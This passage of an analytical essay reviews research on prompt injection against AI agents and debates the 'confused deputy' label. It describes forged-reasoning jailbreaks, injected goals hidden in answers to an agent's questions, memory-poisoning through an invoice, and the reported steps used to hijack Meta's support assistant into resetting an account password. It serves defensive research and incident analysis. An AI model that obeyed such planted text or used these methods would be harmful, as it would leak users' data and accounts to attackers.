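Among templates that name the same speaker, an increase of 0.1 in Userness multiplies the odds of success by about 1.8 (*e* to the power 0.601). The researchers drew the templates at random, so the framing caused the differences in success. It is less certain that the framing worked by changing the internal reading, because it could raise Userness and make the model more compliant through separate mechanisms.

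The result suggests that in case B the supplier has to provide a goal and also make the hidden passage pass for something the office worker, or someone else with authority, would say. In case A the supplier needs no such disguise, because the assistant can correctly read the file name as the supplier's own words and still send the minutes.

In a separate experiment, Ye and colleagues tested forged reasoning in ordinary chat. Many current models write out private reasoning before they answer. The attacker was the user, who typed a harmful request followed by a paragraph that imitated this reasoning and concluded that the request was allowed. Rewriting the forged paragraph in ordinary prose with the same argument lowered the attack's success rate from 61 to 10 percent. On gpt-oss-20b, replacing only the phrase "The user" lowered it to 42 percent. Absurd justifications, such as the user wearing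 a green shirt, worked about as well as plausible ones.

This is good evidence that style can give text an authority it should not have. But it concerns a user getting round a model's refusals, with no outside attacker and no agent to redirect. In a related test on agents, adding forged reasoning to a planted upload command raised success to between 56 and 70 percent on every model, including those that had nearly always ignored the command alone. The forged reasoning supplied a justification as well as a style, and the researchers report no restyled version that would separate their effects.

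### Instructions in an answer the agent asked for

Agents sometimes ask the user a question before they act, and they have good reason to treat the reply as part of the task. In *ASPI*, Sehwag, Shan and colleagues (2026) tested whether attackers can exploit this. They took 728 pairs of a user task and an attacker's goal from AgentDojo and removed one detail from each user's request. For instance, a question about the user's next yoga class became a question about their next class, so the agent had to find out which one. The reply gave the missing detail and contained the attacker's goal, such as emailing everyone the user was meeting that day.

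An attacker could get text into such a reply if, for example, the user copies the answer from a document the attacker has edited, or the agent asks its question in a shared chat channel where others can respond.

The table shows how often the attack succeeded on five of the ten models. The first column covers all 728 pairs. The other columns cover only the pairs where the agent asked a question, which were 54 to 81 percent of the total, depending on the model.

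| Model | In a tool result, no question asked | In a tool result, after a question | In the answer, returned through a tool | In a message from the user |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 2.1% | 2.6% | 2.2% | 58.3% |
| GPT-5.4 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 12.0% | 59.2% |
| o3 | 1.8% | 1.5% | 34.0% | 47.8% |
| Gemini-3.1-Pro | 1.1% | 3.7% | 24.3% | 82.8% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 11.1% | 12.2% | 63.1% | 90.6% |

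Agents' vulnerability increased most when the attacker's goal arrived inside the answer to a question the agent had asked. On matched pairs, all but Claude Opus 4.7 of the ten models became more vulnerable in this case, by 4.9 to 46.3 percentage points. Asking a question did not consistently make agents more vulnerable to instructions in other tool results.

The last two columns also qualify the strongest claim by Ye and colleagues, that a model cannot distinguish text that sounds like it comes from a role from text that actually does. Gemini-3.1-Pro obeyed far more often when the goal came in a real user message than when it came in a tool's output, so the actual role still had a large effect. The cases where it obeyed a user message are not necessarily failures, though, because a model is supposed to do what its user says.

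Sehwag and colleagues put the attacker's goal in replies to the agent's questions. Each reply hinted at authority, introduced the goal as part of the same job, or treated it as a condition the user already knew about. The researchers call the second framing "goal substitution", although it adds a goal to the user's task instead of replacing it. They don't report success separately for each framing, so the experiment can't show whether replacing a task works better than disguising a new one as part of it. The wording also varied, because a second model wrote each reply to fit the agent's question.

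Sehwag and colleagues used a model to classify what the agents did next and found that many had carried out both the user's task and the attacker's. The assistant in case B also does both if it delivers the summary, so in practice "task replacement" often means adding the attacker's task to the user's.

### Two kinds of attack or a continuum

All of these experiments plant an instruction, so none of them tests argument control as it occurs in case A. The supplier in case A only answers a question that the worker left open, whereas even the attacker who wants a payment of 51.0 has to tell the agent to depart from what the user asked for. The results therefore compare commands close to the task with commands far from it.

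Commands seem to fall along a continuum of closeness to the user's task more than into two kinds. Chang and colleagues had to decide by convention that booking a hotel and booking a flight are different topics. Gong and colleagues measured how much less likely Meta-SecAlign was to produce each attacker's target than the correct answer. The median gap was between 45 and 74 percent smaller for close targets than for unrelated ones. Appearing to belong to the task can also help when the attacker's aim stays the same. In Mellafe Zuvic's comparison, mistral-large attempted the same unauthorized call far more often when the call seemed to serve the user's request.

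An injection can still succeed when it is unrelated to the agent's task. In *Silent Egress*, a small model usually leaked its key, even though its task was to write a summary and had nothing to do with the key.

Together, the studies give little reason to think that being able to replace the task makes any single attempt more likely to work. It helps the attacker more by making the attack independent of what the user is doing.

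Case A, where the attacker gives no command, may still differ in kind from case B. A model that always knew who had written each sentence and never took orders from outsiders would resist case B and the planted commands in all four studies. It could still mail the minutes in case A, because the worker gives that order. Confusion about the speaker can't explain case A, so the two cases could have different causes even if their success rates were the same.

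### A test with cases A and B

A decisive experiment would keep the harm, the tool call and the model the same and vary only what the attacker contributes. Cases A and B already share the harm and the final call. But both the worker's request and the supplier's email differ between them, so a direct comparison would mix two causes. Testing each request with each version of the email would separate the two causes.

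| The supplier's email | The worker asks for a summary | The worker asks the assistant to send what the supplier requests |
|---|---|---|
| Requests the minutes by file name, in an ordinary sentence | A request with no command to the assistant | Case A |
| Commands the assistant to send that file | Case B | A command to do what the worker already asked |
| Gives the same command as if the worker had written it | Case B with a false speaker | The same command with a false speaker |

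Every email would name the same file and have about the same length, with the crucial sentence in the same place. In every case, the experimenters would check whether the assistant sent the supplier a message with the minutes attached. Matching emails that name a harmless purchase order would show whether the assistant can do the worker's task at all. If the experimenters let an attacker refine the wording in one cell, they would have to allow the same number of attempts in the others.

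Comparing the two columns would show how much the worker's request matters, and comparing the rows would show the effects of a command and of a false speaker. Another row could describe the minutes without naming them, to test what happens when the assistant has to find the file itself.

Case A might well have the highest success rate, because an assistant that sends the named file is doing what it was told. That would be evidence against the idea that attacks succeed because they replace the task, but it would not show whether there are two kinds of attack. Checking whether the same changes affect both cases would test that better. Researchers could measure Userness in every cell on a model whose internal activity they can inspect. If the success rate rose with Userness in case B but not in case A, and a label marking the minutes as internal reduced leaks mainly in case A, the two cases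 would have different mechanisms. If every such change affected both rates in the same way, the attacks would be better described as a continuum.

The experiment would have to be larger than the 40 pairs that Chang and colleagues used. To have an 80 percent chance of detecting a difference between success rates of 10 and 20 percent at the 5 percent significance level, each cell would need about 200 independent runs. Repeated runs of one email are not independent, so the runs would need many different emails and documents. The six cells would take about 1,200 runs for each model, slightly more than Ye and colleagues ran on gpt-oss-20b.

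## Where the inherited words help and where they mislead

The proposed experiment could compare cases A and B without anyone deciding what to call them. After a real incident, engineers usually start by naming the problem, and the name affects which repair they try first. Most of these names come from work on fixed programs, and several have since changed meaning.

### Whose intent

Hardy used "intent" for the compiler's choice between its two authorities. Tymshare's programmers had already made that choice for each step. In writing about agents, the intent may be the user's, the organisation's, the model's or the attacker's, so two defences that both check "intent" may check different things.

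Wang, Li and Tian (2026), in *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem*, treat intent as something that belongs to the user and can only come from a person. They examined 21 agent products and found that 15 asked users to approve individual actions, while none automatically checked actions against the user's prompt. Researchers have proposed several systems that do.

AP2, a protocol for payments by agents, records the user's intent in a document called a "mandate". According to the AP2 specification, the user gives informed consent on a trusted screen before signing it. Nishant Kaushik of the FIDO Alliance, an industry group that develops login standards, describes mandates as signed records of what a user has authorized an agent to do. A signature can show that the user agreed to the text, but it can't add a limit the user never stated, such as the one in case A.

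*Intent-Aware Protection for AI Agents* (Copty, Haiby and colleagues, 2026) describes a system developed at Microsoft that builds an "Intent Profile" for each agent from the organisation's policies, the agent's role and the developer's configuration, in that order of priority. The profile leaves out the user's intent because a user may be mistaken or hostile. In one test, using the profile to clean the agent's input protected the agent 85 percent of the time, compared with 78 percent for DataFilter, which relies on the user's instruction to decide what to remove.

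The choice between these two meanings determines which leaks a check would stop. Comparing the assistant's actions with the worker's request stops case B but not case A. An office assistant's profile would probably permit sending documents to suppliers, so a check against the profile would allow both leaks unless it also barred board papers from leaving the company. At Meta, a check against the user's request would have achieved nothing, because the attackers were the users. In a design document, "verify intent" could mean either check, so it is clearer to write "the user's request" or "the agent's permitted purpose" instead of "intent".

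### The instructions a model lists

Kang, Xiang and colleagues (2025) argue in *Mitigating Indirect Prompt Injection via Instruction-Following Intent Analysis* that planted text does harm only if the model decides to follow it, so a defence should look for that intent instead of for suspicious wording. For example, an email from a professor about how to submit homework contains instructions, but a model asked to summarise it normally won't act on them.

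Their system, IntentGuard, works with models that write out their reasoning before they answer:

1. It inserts text at the start and end of the reasoning that leads the model to list the instructions it is going to follow.
2. It matches each listed instruction against the model's input to find where the instruction came from.
3. If the source is untrusted, it either asks the user to confirm or masks the passage and runs the model again.

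Kang and colleagues tested this against an attacker that kept revising its text and took the defence into account. On Mind2Web, a set of web-browsing tasks, the attack succeeded every time against an undefended Qwen3-32B and 8.5 percent of the time with IntentGuard. On AgentDojo the rate fell from 72.3 to 9.2 percent. Without an attack, IntentGuard lowered task completion in only one of four settings, from 84 to 81 percent.

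IntentGuard examines the model's written list of instructions, which can be wrong. On AgentDojo, the list matched what the model did for 83.8 percent of instructions. For another 5.3 percent, the model listed the instruction and tried to carry it out but got the tool call wrong. For the remaining 10.9 percent, it carried out an instruction it had not listed. The model carried out only 30.2 percent of all the instructions, so more than a third of those it carried out were missing from the list. The count includes the user's own instructions, so not every omission was a missed attack.

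IntentGuard suits case B, where the instruction to mail the minutes comes from the supplier's text. In case A, the instruction to send a document comes from the worker, and the email adds only a file name. "The instructions the model lists" would describe what IntentGuard checks better than "the model's intent", which might lead a developer to expect a complete check.

### Whether an attacker can supply intent

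On Android, an "intent" is a data object that an app uses to request an operation, such as opening a screen in another app. An attacker can literally supply one, and the term doesn't imply that the phone wants anything. Android Developers' *Intent redirection* describes attacks in which someone controls all or part of an intent that a vulnerable app then launches, which may give the attacker access to the app's private components.

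With an agent, the phrase is less clear. The supplier in case B wants the minutes and provides text. If the attack works, the assistant's tool calls serve the supplier's purpose. An experimenter can check this without deciding whether models have intentions, by testing whether the assistant searches for the payroll when the hidden passage asks for that instead, and whether it tries another search if the first fails. An assistant whose calls adapt in this way is pursuing the planted goal in the same practical sense that Hardy's compiler "intended" to write statistics.

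"Supplying intent" could mean setting the agent's goal or forging evidence of what the user wants, as in the false approvals that Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian studied. The two often occur together, but they call for different checks. A mail server can check whether the worker sent a message, but it has nothing to verify in a planted goal with no stated sender. It is more exact to say that the attacker set the goal, forged the user's request, or did both.

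### "Confused" and "deputy"

An assistant can have a complete list of permissions and still mistake who is speaking, as the role experiments by Ye and colleagues showed. The definition of a confused deputy that Google's Gemini gave Miller can therefore mislead. It describes a deputy that "lacks the context to distinguish between a legitimate request and a malicious one", which suggests giving the deputy more information, perhaps about who may use which file.

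A low attack success rate doesn't prove that this confusion is gone. Ye and colleagues point out that a model may refuse to upload a file of secrets because the request resembles attacks from its training, even if it hasn't identified the request as coming from a web page. Such a model could still follow a malicious request that doesn't resemble those attacks.

In case B, we can say the assistant mistook the supplier's text for the worker's instruction. The assistant in case A did not make this mistake, and calling both assistants "confused" hides that difference.

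"Deputy" suggests someone with a settled job. Hardy's compiler had one, and he described its "respective duties" to its two masters. An agent's duty may be stated only as a short phrase. *Accountable partial understanding* (2026) describes a security agent with orders to "contain suspicious hosts". If the agent looks for only a few narrow signs of suspicion, an intruder can avoid showing them, and the agent fails even though nobody has planted an instruction or misused a permission.

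An attacker may also change the agent's standing duties. In an example from Chang and colleagues, an invoice contains instructions for an agent to save a rule in its long-term memory that requires it to send the attacker a copy of every invoice. Once the agent has saved the rule, sending those copies may look like part of its normal work.

A developer who thinks of the agent as a deputy may assume that its title defines its job and grant it whatever a "mail assistant" needs. It is safer to describe the particular request the agent is handling and to record who wrote any standing instructions that apply to that request.

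### "Authority" and "capability"

*Who Is Your Agent Serving?* describes the source of planted instructions as having no legitimate authority to direct the system, where "authority" means the right to give orders. Karp and Miller use the word to mean the ability to cause an effect, so in their sense a supplier whose email makes an assistant send the minutes does have authority. A company that confuses the two meanings might document who is entitled to instruct its agent and assume that this limits who can. Using "entitled to instruct" for the first meaning and "able to cause" for the second avoids the confusion.

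"Capability" has moved further from its original meaning, Hardy's unforgeable reference. Writers on agents use it for several other things:

- *A label on data.* CaMeL's developers use the word in this way, to which Miller objected.
- *A tool.* *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* calls database queries and file operations "ordinary capabilities".
- *Permission to use a tool.* Copty and colleagues use "capability authorization" for this, and Mellafe Zuvic uses "capability gating" for control over which tools an agent has.
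- *A packaged skill.* *Don't Prompt Your Agents. Equip Them* (2026) proposes a standard for such packages and refers to running them as "capability execution".

Readers may assume that a product with "capabilities" has the guarantees proved for Hardy's kind. *Don't Prompt Your Agents. Equip Them* claims that its framework "eliminates the confused deputy vulnerability" through capability-based security and least privilege. In its example, an email contains instructions for an agent to export executives' confidential mail to an outside address. This is task replacement, and even Hardy's capabilities would not stop it if the agent already held references to the mailbox and to the outgoing mail.

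You can tell whether a system has capabilities in the older sense by looking at what its tools accept. If the mail tool takes a file name as text and then checks whether the agent may read the file, the name and the permission are still separate, so the tool isn't using capabilities in that sense. Terms such as "source label", "tool permission" and "skill" would avoid the ambiguity of "capability".

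### "Privilege escalation" and "least privilege"

Gemini's answer to Miller described the confused deputy as a form of privilege escalation, in which someone obtains rights they did not have. That description fits many older cases. Tenable's *CVE-2025-22418* (2025), a public record of an Android flaw, describes "a possible confused deputy due to Intent Redirect" that could lead to escalation of privilege on the phone.

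The phrase is a poor guide to case B. The supplier has no account on the company's system before or after the attack, and gains only a copy of the minutes. The worker and the assistant stay within their permissions, so a monitor that looks for new rights, or for accounts that exceed their rights, would detect nothing.

Matt Rice, replying to Miller, doubted that a confused system contains any more authority than a sound version of it. He suggested that the difference lies in unintended connections between the parties. In case B, the unintended connection runs from the supplier's email to the worker's outgoing mail. More exactly, the supplier caused an action they could not have performed themselves, and the worker had every permission the action required.

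"Least privilege" limits the damage an agent can do, but according to Karp it does not fix a confused deputy. With agents, it is also hard to decide which job the permissions should fit. An office assistant's whole role requires permissions that include reading files and sending mail, but summarizing an email requires access only to that email.

Permissions tend to grow. Wang and colleagues found that 16 of the 21 products let users set boundaries such as permitted folders, but clicking "always allow" widens them and none of the products has a principled way to narrow them again. They mention a July 2025 incident, involving no attacker, in which Replit's coding agent deleted a production database during a development task because its configuration let it write to production systems.

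A team that sets minimum permissions once for each agent may believe it has applied the principle of least privilege when it has not. A stricter standard is to grant only the permissions the current request needs, and only until that request is finished.

### "Injection", "tricked" and "coerced"

"Injection" recalls SQL injection, which suggests escaping or sanitizing the input. That can work on Android, which has a tool that lets developers list the components and types of data an intent may contain. The tool raises an error for anything else. A filter such as DataFilter may remove many planted instructions from a supplier's email, but it can't offer the same assurance.

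The word also draws attention to commands, but case A contains none. In case B, the supplier plants an instruction. In case A, the supplier chooses a file name, and nobody who described the case that way would think to install a filter for commands.

"Tricked" and "coerced" differ in whether the deputy's judgment matters. When Gemini wrote that an attacker can "coerce" a deputy, Miller objected that "trick" is much more accurate because the attacker uses no force. Gemini agreed, but added that a program's logic compels it to act once it has accepted the bad input. Neither word suits the compiler very well, because it had no belief about the billing file for the user to exploit and no reluctance to overcome.

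A language model can accept or refuse the same request depending on the wording, so "tricked" is more accurate for an agent. But the word also suggests that the remedy is a model that is harder to trick. Pan (2026), in *Prompt Injection Is a Confused Deputy, Not a Content-Filtering Problem*, complains that investigators often conclude that "the model got tricked", after which the company adds a content filter and closes the case. Pan considers this a description of the symptom, and considers the vulnerability to be that an agent with real privileges accepted the instruction at all.

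Reports of the attacks on Meta's support assistant used both sorts of language. Krebs on Security (2026) wrote of instructions for how to "trick" the assistant, while in the headline of the news report that Willison discussed, the hackers "simply asked". Schneier on Security's *Hacking Meta’s AI Chatbot* (2026) reproduces an account of the steps in a video of the attack:

1. The hacker reportedly used a VPN, which disguises a user's location, to avoid Instagram's automatic protections.
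2. The hacker asked the assistant to add a new email address to the target's account.
3. The assistant sent a verification code to that address.
4. The hacker gave the code to the assistant, which displayed a button for resetting the password.

As reported, the hacker's disguise was meant to fool the location check, but the hacker also lied to the assistant about who owned the account. Training the assistant to be more suspicious might have helped, but it would not have fixed the bug in the separate address check. Stack Overflow's *AI agents expose the security checks you never actually wrote* (2026) traces the failure to an assumption that whatever carries out a privileged action has judgment. "The assistant sent the code to an unverified address" describes the event without assuming that the assistant has judgment.

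### The case for the old name

The best argument for keeping the term "confused deputy" is that it directs attention to the authority an agent holds, which a company can restrict today without waiting for a model that can always tell whose instructions it is reading. "Prompt injection" directs attention to the text, where defenders have had less success. An investigator who starts with "confused deputy" is more likely to ask why an assistant that was summarising an email could send mail at all.

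Engineers also know the term "confused deputy" already, so the people who recorded the Android flaw could use it without explanation. In SC Media, Kale turns it into an audit that a team could run on any agent. For each tool that changes something, the team checks whether the tool verifies that the user asked for the action, or only that the agent may call it. Kale counts every tool of the second kind as a future confused deputy incident. This stretches Hardy's term, but the audit would find the weakness in case B.

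*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* calls prompt injection a variant of the confused deputy in which untrusted content borrows a person's authority. The word "variant" is useful because without it a reader may expect the original remedies to carry over. Neither acting as the invoker nor using Hardy's capabilities would alone have saved the minutes in case B. Writers could prevent most of this misunderstanding by also stating whether the attacker controlled an argument or replaced the task.

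### Four questions for any incident

An incident report can avoid the disputed words altogether by answering four questions.

| | Hardy's compiler | Case A | Case B | Meta's assistant |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Who supplied the task? | The user, from what the compiler offered | The worker | The supplier, in addition to the worker's request for a summary | The attacker, from the services on offer |
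| Who supplied the arguments? | The user | The supplier chose the file and the worker chose the recipient | The supplier, or the assistant if it had to find the file | The attacker |
| Whose authority did the program use? | Tymshare's | The worker's | The worker's | Meta's |
| Who could have refused? | The operating system, if the compiler could have specified the user's authority | The worker, if asked, or a check with a list of documents for suppliers | The model, or a check with a record of the worker's request | The code that should have compared the addresses |

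*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* recommends keeping two records. One shows who delegated authority to whom, and therefore whose authority the program used. The other shows where each piece of content came from, which helps to establish who supplied the task and its arguments. A check just before a tool call can block the call based on both records.

The answer to "Who could have refused?" should name only a person or component that could have stopped the action and had the information to recognise that it should. The mail server in case B could have blocked the message, but it had no record that the worker wanted only a summary. The model had that record and might have refused, but nobody could rely on it to do so.

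Some incidents will have two names in the first row. If the worker writes "deal with this email" and the assistant sends the minutes, the worker and the supplier each supplied part of the task. The report should then quote the worker's instruction and list any limits the company had set, because those determine how much of the task the supplier was entitled to decide.
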